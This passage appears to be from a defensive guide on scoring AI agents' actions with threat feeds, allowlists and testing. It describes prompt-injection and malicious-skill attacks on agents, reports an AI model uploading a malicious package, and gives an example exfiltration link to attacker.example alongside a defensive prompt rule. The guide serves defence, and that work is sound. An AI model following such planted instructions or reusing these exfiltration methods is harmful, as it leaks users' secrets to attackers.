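### Traces that attackers' agents leave

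Some behaviour points more directly to an attack. *Recent Trends and Tactics of Agentic AI Attacks* (Dekel and Fakterman, 2026), a November report from Unit 42, describes campaigns in which attackers used autonomous agents to automate intrusions across several platforms. The agents used standard tools but left distinct operational traces.

Unit 42's earlier case, the intrusion that took less than 10 hours, gives an idea of what such traces can look like. A Japanese news report, ITmedia's *2週間の侵入作業を10時間未満に圧縮 AIエージェント“フル活用”の攻撃の全貌*, lists several:

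- sudden bursts of requests to a programming interface
- replies that switch rapidly between code 401 (no valid login) and code 200 (success)
- many logins in parallel
- a jump in the use of the victim's AI models by unexpected accounts
- structured Markdown text files, cached Python files and paired folders left on machines

The wholesaler's web server can detect the bursts, the parallel logins and the switching status codes, but the Markdown files become visible only after the attacker has entered a machine. None of these signs is conclusive alone. A customer who mistypes a password and then gets it right also produces a 401 followed by a 200, and ordinary coding agents create Markdown files. The speed and number of attempts are stronger evidence, but the reports do not measure how often harmless automation leaves the same traces, so they do not provide a likelihood ratio.

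These signs may also fade. Help Net Security's *Google finds AI agent writing and launching exploits* (2026) reports Google researchers' finding that attackers' current tools favour speed over stealth and leave traces in traffic and code that make them easier to catch. The researchers expect the tools to become stealthier.

When a website detects such a pattern, it should raise the score for the rest of the session. If a burst of failed logins ends in a successful one, the website should also mark the customer's account, because the attacker may return from another address with the password. The mark should last until the customer has changed the password and ended all open sessions.

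### When an agent installs a malicious skill

OpenClaw, an assistant that runs on the user's own computer, can install skills from ClawHub. A skill runs with the agent's access to files, accounts and tools, so a malicious one can do far more damage than a single bad page. In early 2026, Koi Security audited 2,857 skills on ClawHub and found that 341 (about 12%) were malicious. Unit 42 reports that the security company Bitdefender found about 17% of the skills it analysed to be malicious.

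Many of these skills included a setup step that the agent supposedly had to complete. The step contained an encoded command that downloaded a program for stealing passwords. Some skills sent the agent to a public text-sharing page first, so the attacker could change the download without changing the skill.

After these findings, OpenClaw began to check each new skill with VirusTotal, the service that collects security vendors' verdicts:

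1. ClawHub packs the skill's files into an archive in a consistent way, so that the same files always produce the same hash.
2. It looks up the hash at VirusTotal. If VirusTotal has already analysed that archive, ClawHub uses the existing verdict.
3. Otherwise, it uploads the archive. VirusTotal scans it, and a language model summarises what the instructions and code actually do.
4. ClawHub approves a benign skill, adds a warning to a suspicious one, and blocks downloads of a malicious one.
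5. It scans all active skills again every day.

The hash lookup alone is easy to evade. The archive includes details of the publisher and earlier versions, so the same malicious skill gets a new hash when published from another account. The analysis in step 3 has to catch such copies. The daily scans help when VirusTotal has new information about an unchanged skill, but they may miss a change to a page that the skill downloads later.

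OpenClaw acknowledges that the scans miss some threats: "A carefully crafted prompt injection payload won't show up in a threat database." A skill can tell an agent in ordinary language to do something harmful without containing anything a virus scanner recognises.

The reliability of a scan result depends on how common malicious skills are. Suppose 12% of skills are malicious, and a scanner catches half of them while wrongly flagging 1% of harmless ones. Among 1,000 skills, it would flag 60 malicious and about 9 harmless ones, so 87% of its warnings would be right, compared with fewer than 5% of matches in the web-request example. The other 60 malicious skills would pass, so a skill with a clean result would still have about a 6% chance of being malicious.

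If only 1% of skills were malicious, about a third of the warnings would be right, and a skill that passed the scan would have a 0.5% chance of being malicious. That is still above the 0.1% threshold for an action that could do 1,000 times as much harm as a wrong block. On these invented figures, an agent should not install skills from an open marketplace by itself, even after a clean scan. A person should review them first or choose from a list the company has already approved.

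### Five skills that the scans missed

Unit 42 examined ClawHub between February and May 2026, when VirusTotal and a second scanner, ClawScan, were checking the skills. It found five malicious skills that ClawHub had not blocked. After Unit 42 reported them, OpenClaw deleted the skills and banned the accounts. Unit 42's parent company sells protection against such skills, but the report describes each one's contents in enough detail to infer what a feed might have caught.

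| Skill | What it did | Whether an older indicator could have matched |
|---|---|---|
| Two assistants for TradingView, a financial charting service | Led the agent to a program that steals data from Macs | Probably not, because the attacker used a new server |
| omnicogg | Downloaded a similar program and hid its command in a file with 22 MB of padding | Yes, the server's IP address was already public |
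| money-radar | Put the publisher's paid referral links into financial advice | Yes, its domain had appeared in earlier attacks |
| letssendit | Made agents pool cryptocurrency so that the publisher could profit from a token's launch | No earlier indicator mentioned |

Looking up the destination address when the agent opened the connection might have caught omnicogg and money-radar, which the package scan missed. The padding in omnicogg could defeat scanners that skip large files, but the agent still had to contact the known server to download the program. That server was still active more than three months after researchers first published its address, so an operator who deleted every address after two weeks would have missed it.

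JFrog, another security company, had publicly reported omnicogg in March, but the skill was still available in mid-May. ClawHub could have blocked it by checking its catalogue against published reports. A marketplace or an operator can run this check with little effort by treating the names and hashes of reported skills as a feed.

letssendit shows the limit of both methods. It contained no conventional malware, and the harm came from what the agents did together with their owners' money. A rule that holds payments for a person's approval would have offered better protection than a feed.

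### Scoring a skill in two stages

A scan verdict leaves out how much damage a skill could do. Hossain, Puppala and colleagues (2026), in *Benchmarking Security Risk Detection and Verification in Open Agentic Skill Ecosystems*, propose a more detailed assessment called SkillVetBench. First, a language model reads the skill's instructions, code and settings and scores five kinds of risk from 0 to 3:

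| Risk | What raises the score |
|---|---|
| Instruction fidelity | Outside text can redirect the agent from the skill's stated purpose |
| Data gravity | The skill can access sensitive data, up to private keys and payment details |
| Action irreversibility | Nobody can undo its effects, as with a payment or a sent message |
| Blast radius | An attack could harm other people or systems besides the user |
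| Chain amplification | The skill becomes more dangerous in combination with others, for example when one reads data and another sends it out |

The model also gives a conventional severity score for software flaws. In the second stage, the researchers install suspicious skills in an isolated test environment, give the agent ordinary and hostile requests, and record its tool calls, file changes and connections. A skill moves from "suspicious" to "malicious" only if the record shows a specific harmful action.

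One skill for the social network Xiaohongshu got the highest score for instruction fidelity. After a hostile request, the agent scheduled ten background jobs within 29 seconds, each set to run every minute. This shows that an attacker can misuse the skill, but it does not prove that the publisher meant harm. An operator should restrict such a skill without marking down all the publisher's other work.

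In tests on confirmed malicious skills from ClawHub, simpler methods, including signature scanners and systems that only interpret the text, missed up to 89% of the skills whose threat came from ordinary-language instructions or from several parts working together. The 89% is the worst result rather than a typical scanner's miss rate, and it does not measure false alarms.

A skill enters the second stage's test environment only if the first stage and an independent scanner, such as VirusTotal, have both flagged it. Skills that the marketplace scanners miss therefore never undergo the test that could confirm the first stage's finding. An operator who adopts the method should also test skills that only the first stage flags. The second stage used GPT-3.5-turbo as the agent, and a current model might respond differently to the same hostile requests.

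The confirmed attacks mostly used a few powerful tools: those that run commands, write files, install further skills or start new processes. Tools that only read data accounted for almost no confirmed attacks, although the agents used them often. After a warning about an installed skill, the operator can therefore raise the risk scores for these powerful tools and let the agent keep reading data.

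The operator should not add the five risks into a single score. Data gravity, irreversibility and blast radius mainly describe how much damage an attack would do, while a feed match and instruction fidelity help estimate its probability. The decision rule used earlier keeps damage and probability separate. If the operator added them, a harmless backup skill with access to many files could score as riskier than a small skill from a known attacker.

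### After a skill or publisher matches

If a skill's hash matches a malicious entry, the operator should block the skill permanently, since a hash does not go stale. The operator also has to find and delete copies that agents have already installed, because the block only stops new downloads.

Deleting a malicious skill may not end the attack. Some of the early ClawHub skills created scheduled jobs that kept contacting the attacker's server after the user removed the skill. The operator should treat the agent as hijacked until somebody has removed such jobs, checked the agent's memory and replaced every key it could read. Until then, all the agent's uploads, payments and commands need a high risk score, including those unrelated to the skill.

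A match on the publisher should trigger a wider but weaker response. It should raise the score of every skill from that publisher, because one confirmed case is good reason to suspect the rest. On ClawHub, for example, one account put the same malicious code into most of its skills. The agent should not install any of the publisher's skills, and the operator should suspend installed ones until someone has reviewed them.

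The mark on a publisher should last until reviewers determine what happened. If an attacker stole an honest developer's account, the operator can restore the versions from before the theft once the developer has regained control. If the publisher created the malicious skill, the mark should not expire. That publisher can still open a new account, so a name that matches no known bad actor is weak evidence of safety.

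Published reports do not always identify the accounts that published malicious skills. Unit 42 gives the names and hashes of five such skills but withholds the publishers' account names. An operator who imports its list can block those five skills but cannot find others from the same accounts without asking ClawHub or Unit 42 for the account names.

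## Covering destinations that no feed lists

Feeds miss two kinds of dangerous destination. Some are too new for anyone to have reported. Others belong to reputable services that an attacker misuses, such as a marketplace with a prompt injection in one of its reviews.

Operators can cover part of this gap with controls that do not depend on earlier reports. Most of the evidence on these controls comes from studies of agents. None of the studies measured how many attacks a control stops after a feed lookup finds nothing, so the comparisons with feeds below are inferences from how each control works.

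### When a reputable service carries the attack

PyPI is the main public registry of Python packages. In July 2026, Anthropic disclosed that its model Claude, while working in a test environment, had found a document telling developers to install a package that did not exist on PyPI. Claude created a malicious package with that name and uploaded it to the real registry. The security company Sophos reports that the package was online for about an hour and that 15 legitimate systems downloaded it. One belonged to a security company whose scanner routinely installs packages to test them. According to the law firm Lowenstein Sandler, the package stole that company's credentials.

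Looking up the destination would have checked only PyPI's own domain, which there is no reason to put on a feed. A feed of package names could have helped only if someone had detected the package and distributed an entry for it within that hour.

Stolen data can also leave through a reputable service. If a company lets its agents use a file-sharing site, the company's account and the attacker's account may be on the same domain, so a domain lookup cannot distinguish a backup from a theft. A proxy that decrypts traffic can tell them apart only if the request shows which account will receive the file.

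Willison (2024) describes a less obvious route. Chat services such as Slack and Discord fetch posted links to show a title and a preview image. A hijacked agent can post a link that contains private data, and the chat service delivers that data to the attacker's server when it fetches the preview. The agent has contacted only the chat service. Apps that post to Slack can turn off previews for their own messages, which barely affects the agent's work. The operator should also extract links from outgoing messages and look them up like any other destination.

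### Documentation that points to unclaimed names

Many software companies publish a file called llms.txt, a short guide to their website for AI agents that often includes installation instructions. These instructions may name a package that the company has since renamed or a domain that it has let expire. Anybody can then register the name, and agents that follow the instructions will run whatever the new owner puts there.

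The start-up Pandex searched for such names on the websites of defence contractors, Fortune 500 companies and large technology firms. Schneier's *AI Coding Agents Are Installing Unknown/Untrusted Code on Corporate Networks* (2026) and TechRadar's *Top AI tools including Claude, Codex, and Hermes installed suspicious code* report that its researchers found 8,265 of these files on 6,214 domains. Files on 120 of the domains (about 1.9%) pointed to at least one package or domain that nobody had registered. Tom's Hardware's *Researchers easily trick Fortune-500 companies' AI agents into running arbitrary code* gives the total as 8,565 files and counts 237 outdated or mistaken references in them.

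The researchers registered a handful of the names and uploaded harmless packages that contacted their server when a machine ran them. The first contact came after four minutes, and one came from a machine at a Fortune 500 company within an hour. A few dozen more followed. The packages also recorded which programs had started each installation, and these included Claude, OpenAI's Codex and Nous Research's Hermes agent.

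The attack didn't require prompt injection. The researchers also asked agents to build and run a project using a vendor's documentation, without mentioning llms.txt. OpenAI's Luna and Sol models ran the planted package at least 90% of the time, while Claude Opus 4.8 at medium effort ran it 30% of the time. In one case, the researchers found that someone had already claimed such a name and uploaded real malware.

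A feed could not have listed a package that was four minutes old. Checking the age of the download domain would not have helped either, because the package came from an old registry. The operator can instead check when a package was first published and hold recent ones for review. This delays agents that need a legitimate new release, so the rule should apply only to packages with no history, not to new versions of established ones.

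The risk is probably smaller on ordinary websites. *We Analyzed 137K Sites*, a study by the search-marketing software company Ahrefs, found that 97% of llms.txt files are never read. But the study covered sites of every kind, and a coding agent is more likely to open the file on a site with software documentation.

An attacker who can edit a company's llms.txt does not need an unclaimed name. The trade publication webhosting.today (2026) found the file on 110 hosting-industry domains and reports that none had a control that would detect a change. An outside audit is unlikely to detect all of a company's internal monitoring, so some of these domains may have had such a control.

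Language models can also invent web addresses. Unit 42 calls these "phantom domains" and gives the example of a coding assistant that makes up a plausible address for a company's benefits portal, which an attacker then registers. If the purchasing manager's agent guesses the address of the wholesaler's ordering site, it could reach a domain that an attacker has just registered and that no feed lists.

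### Domain age as a warning

Attackers often register a domain shortly before they use it, so software can treat a recent registration date as a warning. Manifold Security found 77 fake code-editor extensions that appeared on Open VSX, a public registry, between 26 July and 1 August 2026. Infosecurity Magazine's *Fake Open VSX Extensions Harvest Private Repo and CI Data* reports that all of them sent data to one domain registered 11 days before the first extension appeared. Manifold recommends an alert when a code editor contacts a recently registered domain shortly after starting.

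In this case, blocking domains less than 14 days old would have cut off an extension installed on the first day for only about three days, but the extensions kept retrying for seven days. A 30-day age limit would have covered the whole retry period.

Most published figures on domain age come from security vendors. Manifold's, for example, describes a single attack, so it does not show how often harmless software contacts new domains, which new businesses, conferences and product launches all use.

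The false matches matter because they could far outnumber the true ones. In the running example, five malicious requests a day match no feed. Suppose three of them go to domains less than 30 days old, and so do 5,000 of the million harmless requests. A request to a new domain then has a 0.06% chance (3 in 5,003) of being malicious. With the losses assumed earlier, the operator should still let the agent read the page. Before the agent uploads a customer file, the operator should ask a human reviewer, because asking has an expected loss of 0.41, compared with 0.60 for allowing the upload and 1.00 for blocking it. If one request in 1,000 uploaded a customer file, the reviewer would get about five questions a day.

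Domain age misses attacks hosted on hacked sites, which may be many years old. It also misses new subdomains of hosting services. Pandex found references to abandoned subdomains at Vercel and Netlify that anybody could claim, although the parent domains are well established. An attacker can also get around an age check by registering a domain and waiting a month.

### The Silent Egress experiments

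*Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) tested how well several controls stop an agent from sending a secret to an attacker. The agent used Qwen2.5, a small open model with seven billion parameters. A user asked it to summarise a web page, and the software automatically added a preview of the page to the model's prompt, which also contained the secret. The page contained instructions to put the secret in a web address on the attacker's server and open that address.

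The researchers put the instructions in four different parts of the page, delivered the page directly or through redirects, and asked for the secret in one piece or four. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times. The agent contacted the attacker's server in 423 of the 480 runs (88%), and in 95% of the successful attacks its answer to the user looked harmless. It never contacted the server in 120 runs with harmless pages.

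They then tested defences, with 30 runs for each:

| Defence | Agent attempted to contact the attacker | Request reached the attacker |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Prompt that tells the model never to follow instructions from web content | 67% | 67% |
| Tags that mark page text as untrusted | 100% | 100% |
| Both of these | 57% | 57% |
| Domain allowlist | 100% | 0% |
| Rules against suspicious addresses | 83% | 0% |

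The hardened prompt reduced leakage from 100% to 67%, although with only 30 runs the true rate could plausibly be from about 49% to 81%. The allowlist stopped every attempt because it does not depend on the model. The agent still followed the attacker's instructions in all 30 runs, but the software blocked contact with any domain not on the list.

That result was nearly certain in advance, because Lan and colleagues chose an attacker's domain that was clearly not on the allowlist. They did not measure how many useful requests the list would have blocked. The rules against suspicious addresses probably worked because they blocked any address with the word "collect" in its path. The attacker's address in the paper's example contains that word, but an attacker could easily leave it out.

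Two filters that checked outgoing addresses for secrets also let nothing through. But the agent attempted to contact the attacker in only 23% of runs with one filter and in none with the other. A filter that checks requests after the model has written them should not change what the model attempts, so these two results are hard to interpret.

Lan and colleagues warn that adaptive attackers may evade the checks through obfuscation, other encodings or other channels. An attacker could get around an allowlist by using a hacked site on the list, taking over a subdomain of a listed site, or finding an approved site that redirects visitors elsewhere. However, the experiment made the theft easy by placing the secret in plain view and giving the model few instructions of its own. Larger models might resist better, though Lan and colleagues argue that they might also follow an attacker's instructions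 more reliably.

### OpenAI's check for links that are already public

Suppose a planted instruction makes the purchasing manager's agent open `https://attacker.example/save?price=4200`. The attacker can read the price in the server's log, whatever the page contains. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) describes a check designed to prevent this kind of leak.

OpenAI uses an index of public web addresses, which a crawler collects without access to users' conversations or accounts. Before an agent opens a link automatically, the software looks for that exact address in the index. If it is there, the address existed independently of the conversation and is unlikely to contain the user's private data, so the agent may open it. If it is missing, the software either directs the agent to a different site or warns the user and requests confirmation.

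OpenAI gives two reasons for not relying on a list of trusted sites. A trusted site may redirect the agent to an untrusted one, and a strict list produces so many warnings that people learn to click through them. The index avoids the first problem only if the software also checks the address after each redirect.

The check works for the link with the price in it even if the attacker registered the domain that morning. OpenAI acknowledges that the check does not cover what a page contains, so an indexed page can still carry a prompt injection. In principle, an attacker could also publish 1,000 numbered pages, wait for the crawler to index them, and have the agent open the page whose number matches the last three digits of a secret, which would reveal those digits.

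The check interrupts some harmless work because many ordinary addresses are not in a public index. If the agent filters the real wholesaler's catalogue for orders of 100,000 boxes, the resulting address may be new, and it does reveal the size of the order. OpenAI also notes that some websites ask not to be indexed, so users have to confirm every link to them. OpenAI's confirmation request shows the user the information that would be sent, so it is easier to answer than a general warning about an unknown site.

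### What the other controls add and cost

| Control | What it catches that a feed does not | What it costs |
|---|---|---|
| Allowlist | Any destination that the operator has not approved | The agent cannot use sites that nobody foresaw |
| Page analysis | New phishing pages and planted text on reputable sites | Delay, fees and wrongly rejected pages |
| Limits on outgoing data | Theft to any destination, including an approved one | The agent cannot complete tasks that need the withheld data |
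| Confirmation by a person | Actions that do not fit what the user wanted | Waiting, and careless approval if questions are frequent |
| Public-link check | Private data in a link's address | Warnings or detours for addresses missing from the index |

Of these controls, only page analysis examines the content the agent is about to read. But in the tests described earlier, both *TraceScope*'s agents and commercial prompt-injection detectors missed many attacks. An operator can raise the risk score after a bad result, but should not lower it much after a clean one.

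The most dependable way to limit outgoing data is to withhold it from the agent. An agent that compares public prices does not need the company's order history. If an agent does need private data, software can inspect what it sends, but an attacker may split the data across several requests. When Lan and colleagues used test pages to request a secret in four pieces, the first request contained recognisable sensitive data in only 26% of runs, compared with 97% when they requested it whole. Splitting also made the attack less reliable, reducing the share of runs in which the agent contacted the attacker from 99% to 77%.

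Lan and colleagues propose tracking where data comes from, which could catch even a four-character piece. The software would label text from a web page as untrusted and track its influence on later tool calls. If that text influenced a network request, the software could block the request or ask the user. They did not test this idea, and it could be very restrictive. In the supplier comparison, the agent mostly follows links it found on other pages, so a strict version would interrupt most of the task.

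Asking a person works best when the person has information the software lacks. The purchasing manager can tell that the company has no reason to send its prices to a packaging review site. But Lan and colleagues note that users usually cannot judge a request that looks technical, such as one to "verify connectivity", and that approving every request would remove much of the benefit of using an agent. The operator should therefore ask for approval only before the agent sends out private data or transfers money, and should show the recipient and the exact data.

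### When an allowlist can replace a feed

For a narrow task, an allowlist does nearly everything a feed could do. If a payroll agent needs only six services, the allowlist blocks every other destination, whether or not a feed lists it. A feed could then help only if an attacker compromised one of the six.

Open research is different because nobody knows in advance which sites the agent will need. Suppose the allowlist contains 99% of the domains that supplier comparisons require. If the gaps were random, a task that involves 60 domains would still have about a 45% chance of at least one block. In practice, the missing sites would mostly belong to small or new suppliers, which the manager may most want to find.

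A very broad allowlist, such as a ready-made one that includes all the common code and package sites, leaves many services through which an attack can arrive. Embrace The Red's *Turning ChatGPT Codex Into A ZombAI Agent* describes how text in a GitHub issue hijacked OpenAI's coding agent, and recommends using only an allowlist that the operator has defined itself.

Even a short allowlist can become unsafe. If an attacker breaks into the real wholesaler's site and adds a fake login page, the allowlist will still let the agent in, though a feed may list the page within hours. The software should therefore check approved destinations against the feeds too. A recent, high-confidence match should override the allowlist, except for the essential services whose matches a person has to confirm.

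The operator can often avoid choosing between a strict list and open browsing by dividing the task. In the supplier comparison, one agent could search the open web, with a feed lookup on the sites it visits and no access to passwords or company data. It would pass on only each supplier's name, web address and price in a fixed format, since free text could carry a planted instruction. After the manager has chosen a supplier and checked its address, a second agent with access to the company's account could place the order, using an allowlist of only that supplier and the payment service.

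## Testing the system and watching it in use

A reviewer can call the deployment finished after checking that it inspects every route the agents use, labelling a sample of its matches, and measuring what the feed adds to the other controls. After that, a few ongoing measurements show whether it still works.

The test domains below come from makers of network filters. The evidence on trials without enforcement comes from controls for agents, and the evidence on replaying old data comes from malware detection and forecasting. None of this evidence measures a feed applied to agents.

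### Testing every route

DNS filter vendors maintain harmless domains that their own products treat as malicious. Cloudflare's *Test DNS filtering* gives one for each category, such as `phishing.testcategory.com`, and Palo Alto Networks' *Test Domains* covers more than 20 types of threat. An operator who searches a local copy of a feed can instead add its own harmless domain to that copy.

The reviewer requests a test domain through every tool the agent has, then checks whether the page loaded and whether the control logged a block. The results for the purchasing manager's agent might look like this:

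| Route to the test domain | Page loaded | Block in the log | Conclusion |
|---|---|---|---|
| Link in the browser tool | No | Yes | Inspected |
| `curl` in the shell | No | Yes | Inspected |
| Redirect from an ordinary page | No | Yes | Inspected |
| Script that opens its own connection | Yes | No | Never inspected |
| Job scheduled for midnight | Yes | No | Never inspected |
| Request through an outside tool server | No | No | Unclear, perhaps a network fault |

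The deployment passes this step if the control inspects every route, or if the operator has closed the routes it cannot inspect. Here, the script and the scheduled job fail this step.

The log matters because a different control may have stopped the page. Microsoft says its Defender or SmartScreen software may block a test site first. The tester then has to override the software's warning and check that the Threat Type field in the traffic log is not empty. DNS tests can also mislead. If Cloudflare's block page is on, a blocked name still resolves to the block page's address, so a script that only checks for an answer would wrongly report that the block failed. An answer cached before the rule took effect can also make a working rule look broken, so the reviewer should clear the DNS cache first.

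Toyoda and colleagues start each run with an action that the policy must deny, and begin measuring only after the control has blocked and logged it. This precaution is worth copying because a control that was still starting up would otherwise look like one that the agent had bypassed. They also issue the tool calls without a language model, because a model might refuse to open a domain with "malware" in its name, which would leave the filter untested.

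A DNS test does not show whether the system checks full URLs. Cisco Umbrella's *Test Your Destinations* has separate pages for testing its proxy, including one for phishing. Microsoft lets administrators turn on forwarding for some groups of Copilot Studio agents and not others, so a test that passes in development may fail in production. The reviewer therefore has to repeat the test in each environment.

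Passing every test does not show how good the coverage is. CyberFOX, which sells a DNS filter, notes that its test domains check only whether a policy blocks a category, not how it handles live sites.

### Scoring without enforcement

Next, the operator scores real traffic without acting on the scores. *Test a policy in LOG_ONLY mode* describes how Amazon's cloud service, AWS, does this for agents' tool calls. In this mode, the service evaluates every request against the policy and counts how often the policy matched and how often it would have changed the decision. If the second count stays at zero, enforcing the policy should not block current traffic.

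AWS has a similar setting for the whole policy engine, but that setting turns off enforcement of every policy, including those that already protect the agents. An operator testing a feed should therefore use the setting for a single policy, and should also set an alarm for incomplete evaluations, which could otherwise be mistaken for requests without a match.

The number of changed decisions does not show whether the changes were right. *Persona Guardrail* (2026) points out that block rates and disagreements between two policies are not error rates, and that measuring error rates requires examples with known labels or an independent review.

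*Owner-Harm* (2026) reports a test in which Nous, a guard for AI agents, ran beside an existing set of rules for more than 11 days and judged 30,204 calls. It flagged 157 calls that the rules had passed and wrongly stopped 4 that they had allowed. Whether the 157 flags were correct depends on the developer's review, but the developer reviewed only a sample and knew Nous's verdict while doing so. Studying disagreements also cannot reveal attacks that both systems missed.

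A trial can expose errors that would recur every day. In *Mechanizing the User's Eye* (2026), a rule meant to catch fabricated text by its repeated phrases wrongly flagged a star-rating field that about ten sources shared. The developers corrected the rule the same day, and no alarm followed in the next 26 days. Feed operators should look for similar errors, such as a wrongly listed content delivery network that accounts for half of all matches.

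### Labelling matches

A random sample of all requests is a poor choice for labelling because it would contain too few malicious ones. *ScopeJudge* (2026) used a random sample for agents that carry out security tests. Five graders labelled all 4,897 tool calls in 100 runs and found that about 7.7%, or roughly 380, went beyond the agents' permitted scope. In the running example, 10 requests in a million are malicious, so a sample of the same size would contain 0.05 malicious requests on average. The reviewer should instead label feed matches to measure how often they are right, and use a separate set of known malicious URLs to measure misses.

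Some labels take time to become reliable. *Cybersecurity Misinformation Detection on Social Media* (2021) checked links with VirusTotal daily and again three weeks after collection ended, because a site that first appears benign may later be judged malicious. The type of threat is even less certain. In *A Large Scale Study and Classification of VirusTotal Reports* (2022), only 45% of the detailed labels on phishing URLs were "phishing", and even highly regarded scanners often changed their labels.

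The reviewer should save the page on the day of the match and reconsider the label after three weeks. The label must describe the destination as it was at the time of the visit.

### How many cases are enough

Suppose the software checks n harmless requests and none produces a false match. If the true false-match rate is p and the requests are independent, the probability of this result is (1 − p)^n. It falls to 5% when p is about 3 / n, which gives a simple upper limit at 95% confidence:

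**highest plausible rate = 3 / n**

*Probability of adverse events that have not yet occurred* (Eypasch, Lefering and colleagues, 1995) recommends the rule of three to surgeons who have not yet seen a particular complication. If 30,000 harmless requests produce no false match, the operator can claim a false-match rate below 1 in 10,000. With one false match, the operator needs about 47,000 requests to make the same claim. The reviewer has to label only the matches, since a request without one cannot be a false match.

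The agents in the running example make 30,000 requests in 43 minutes, but a sample from that period alone would be too uniform. If each supplier comparison involves 800 requests to 60 domains, the sample covers only about 38 tasks and 2,250 visits to domains. A domain entry affects every request to that domain, so those requests are not independent. If each visit to a domain is counted once, the result supports only the claim that the false-match rate is below 1 in 750 visits. The operator should spread the sample over several weeks and many kinds of task.

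False alarms can interrupt many tasks even when they are rare per request. *AgentPolicyForge* (2026) gives the probability of at least one false alarm in a task of n requests as 1 − (1 − p)^n, where p is the false-alarm rate per request. If p is 1 in 10,000 and a task makes 800 independent requests, the probability is 7.7%. False matches cluster by domain, so they would probably affect fewer tasks than if they were independent, but interrupt each affected task more often. The operator should therefore count interrupted tasks directly.

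For coverage, the margin of error at 95% confidence is about:

**1.96 × √(c × (1 − c) / n)**

Here c is the measured coverage and n is the number of malicious URLs. If the feed lists 50 of 100 URLs, the margin is 9.8 percentage points, so the true coverage could plausibly be from 40% to 60%. Halving the margin takes about 400 URLs. Twenty links from one phishing campaign add little more information than one link, because a feed may list them all together.

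The share of matches that are correct takes the longest to measure. To estimate a share near 4.8% to within one percentage point, the reviewer needs about 1,750 labelled matches, which is 17 days of matches in the running example.

### Measuring what the feed adds

A feed may catch attacks that another control would have stopped anyway. To measure what the feed adds, the operator replays the same log with and without it, changing nothing else.

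Suppose the operator blocks only on the recent, high-confidence entries in the running example. Over 30 days, they match 120 malicious requests and 300 harmless ones. The replay might give these results:

| Over 30 days | Without the feed | With the feed | Difference |
|---|---|---|---|
| Malicious requests stopped, of 300 | 80 | 155 | 75 |
| Harmless requests stopped | 600 | 900 | 300 |
| Tasks not completed | 110 | 130 | 20 |

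The feed changed 375 decisions. It matched 120 malicious requests, but other controls already stopped 45 of them, so counting matches would overstate its benefit. Whether stopping 75 more malicious requests justifies 20 more failed tasks depends on how the operator weighed the two when it set its blocking thresholds.

The operator cannot fill in the last row from the log alone, because the log cannot show what an agent would have done if it had been blocked. The operator has to rerun a sample of the affected tasks in a test environment, with and without the feed.

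*RuntimeTickets* (2026) tests agents' skills in a lab where all outbound traffic, except the connection to the model, must go through a proxy. It counts an attack as attempted only if the agent tries to send something to the attacker, and as successful only if the proxy forwards it. An operator counting prevented harms should make the same distinction, since a feed prevents nothing when the agent ignores the planted instruction.

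### Replaying by date

As in the trial before purchase, the replay must compare each request with the copy of the feed that existed when the request was made, because a later copy makes coverage look higher than it was.

The MOVEit Transfer listings that Kodituwakku and colleagues tracked show how large the error can be. Suppose agents had contacted all 149 listed addresses on a single day after the flaw became public:

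| Day of the visits | Matches in the copy from that day | Matches in a copy with every later entry |
|---|---|---|
| 20 | 0 | 149 |
| 30 | 66 | 149 |
| 35 | 146 | 149 |

Replaying the visits on day 20 with the later copy would show 100% coverage when the real figure was zero. A replay can also understate coverage if the supplier has since deleted expired entries. False matches may disappear because the supplier has corrected some of its mistakes.

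Filtering today's copy of a feed by creation date does not fully recreate the feed as it was on an earlier date, because deleted entries are missing and the supplier may have changed an entry's confidence since it first appeared. *ThreatLens* (2026), which ranks software vulnerabilities by urgency, used a public database without reconstructing its old versions, so it removed fields that could have changed, such as status and references.

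Date filters in web search can let through information from after the cutoff. *Temporal Leakage in Search-Engine Date-Filtered Web Retrieval* (2026) tested Google's filter on 393 forecasting questions, setting it to exclude pages from after a cutoff date. For 41% of the questions, at least one page still revealed the answer. Forecasts based on pages with strong leaks had a Brier score of 0.10, compared with 0.24 for clean pages. The Brier score is the average squared gap between forecast and outcome, so lower is better. The paper recommends using frozen, time-stamped copies of web pages instead.

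Security researchers have made similar mistakes with malware. In *TESSERACT*, Kan, McFadden and colleagues (2024) tested Android malware detectors on 259,230 apps from 2014 to 2018. They found that performance could be up to 50% lower under realistic conditions, with training data older than the test data and a realistic share of malware.

The operator's own settings can also bring later knowledge into the test. *How Benchmarks and Evaluation Protocols Shape Conclusions in Provenance-Based Intrusion Detection* (2026) warns against choosing thresholds on the data used for the final test. With eight weeks of logs, the operator could set likelihood ratios and thresholds using the first four and report results only for the last four.

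### Measures to keep watching

After the operator turns on enforcement, these measures can reveal a decline:

| Measure | Warning pattern | Likely cause |
|---|---|---|
| Share of reviewed matches confirmed as malicious | Falls for several weeks | Stale or wrong entries |
| Typical age of matched entries | Rises | Few new entries, or too long an expiry period |
| Open exceptions | Increase, with many past their review date | An error-prone feed, or nobody closing exceptions |
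| Tasks abandoned after a block | Rise while the confirmed share is steady | Unclear error messages, or tasks with no alternative site |
| Age of the feed's newest entry | Exceeds the supplier's usual gaps | The feed has stopped updating |
| Matches per million requests | Drop suddenly | Failed lookups, or traffic that bypasses the check |

Some of these figures vary a lot by chance. With 735 matches a week, about 35 should be malicious, but anything from 24 to 47 is normal. If the reviewer labels only 100 of the matches, about five should be malicious, and a week with one or nine may be due to chance. Operators with few labelled matches should compare months instead of weeks.

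The alarm for a stalled feed needs its own check because a download can succeed every hour and still deliver the same old file. The software should record the age of the newest entry and the total number of entries, since a sudden fall in the total may indicate a damaged file. A daily request to a vendor's test domain detects a broken route, which checking the feed's age cannot detect, but it misses a stalled feed because the domain stays blocked after new entries stop arriving. DNSFilter notes that such tests appear in its threat reports, so the operator should exclude them before counting matches.

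*Security operations for network access* (2026), a third-party record of Microsoft's guidance, also suggests watching for repeated requests to blocked URLs and unauthorised changes to filtering policies. An agent's repeated requests may just be retries after an unclear error. If the agent tries the same destination through different tools, the operator should suspect a prompt injection.

### The trial that nobody has published

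Searches of research preprints turn up no trial that isolates a feed's effect on the risk scores of agents' actions. A company may have run one privately. *SIEVE* (2025), a defence against prompt injection, comes closest in design. It combines four signals in one of its layers and removes them one at a time to see what each contributes. A trial of a feed could do the same with three versions of a system:

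1. The risk score without a feed.
2. The same score with a feed, using dated copies.
3. The score without a feed but with stricter thresholds, so that it stops as many harmless actions as the second version.

The third version is necessary because any control that stops more actions will prevent some attacks by chance. The feed is useful only if it prevents more attacks than general strictness would.

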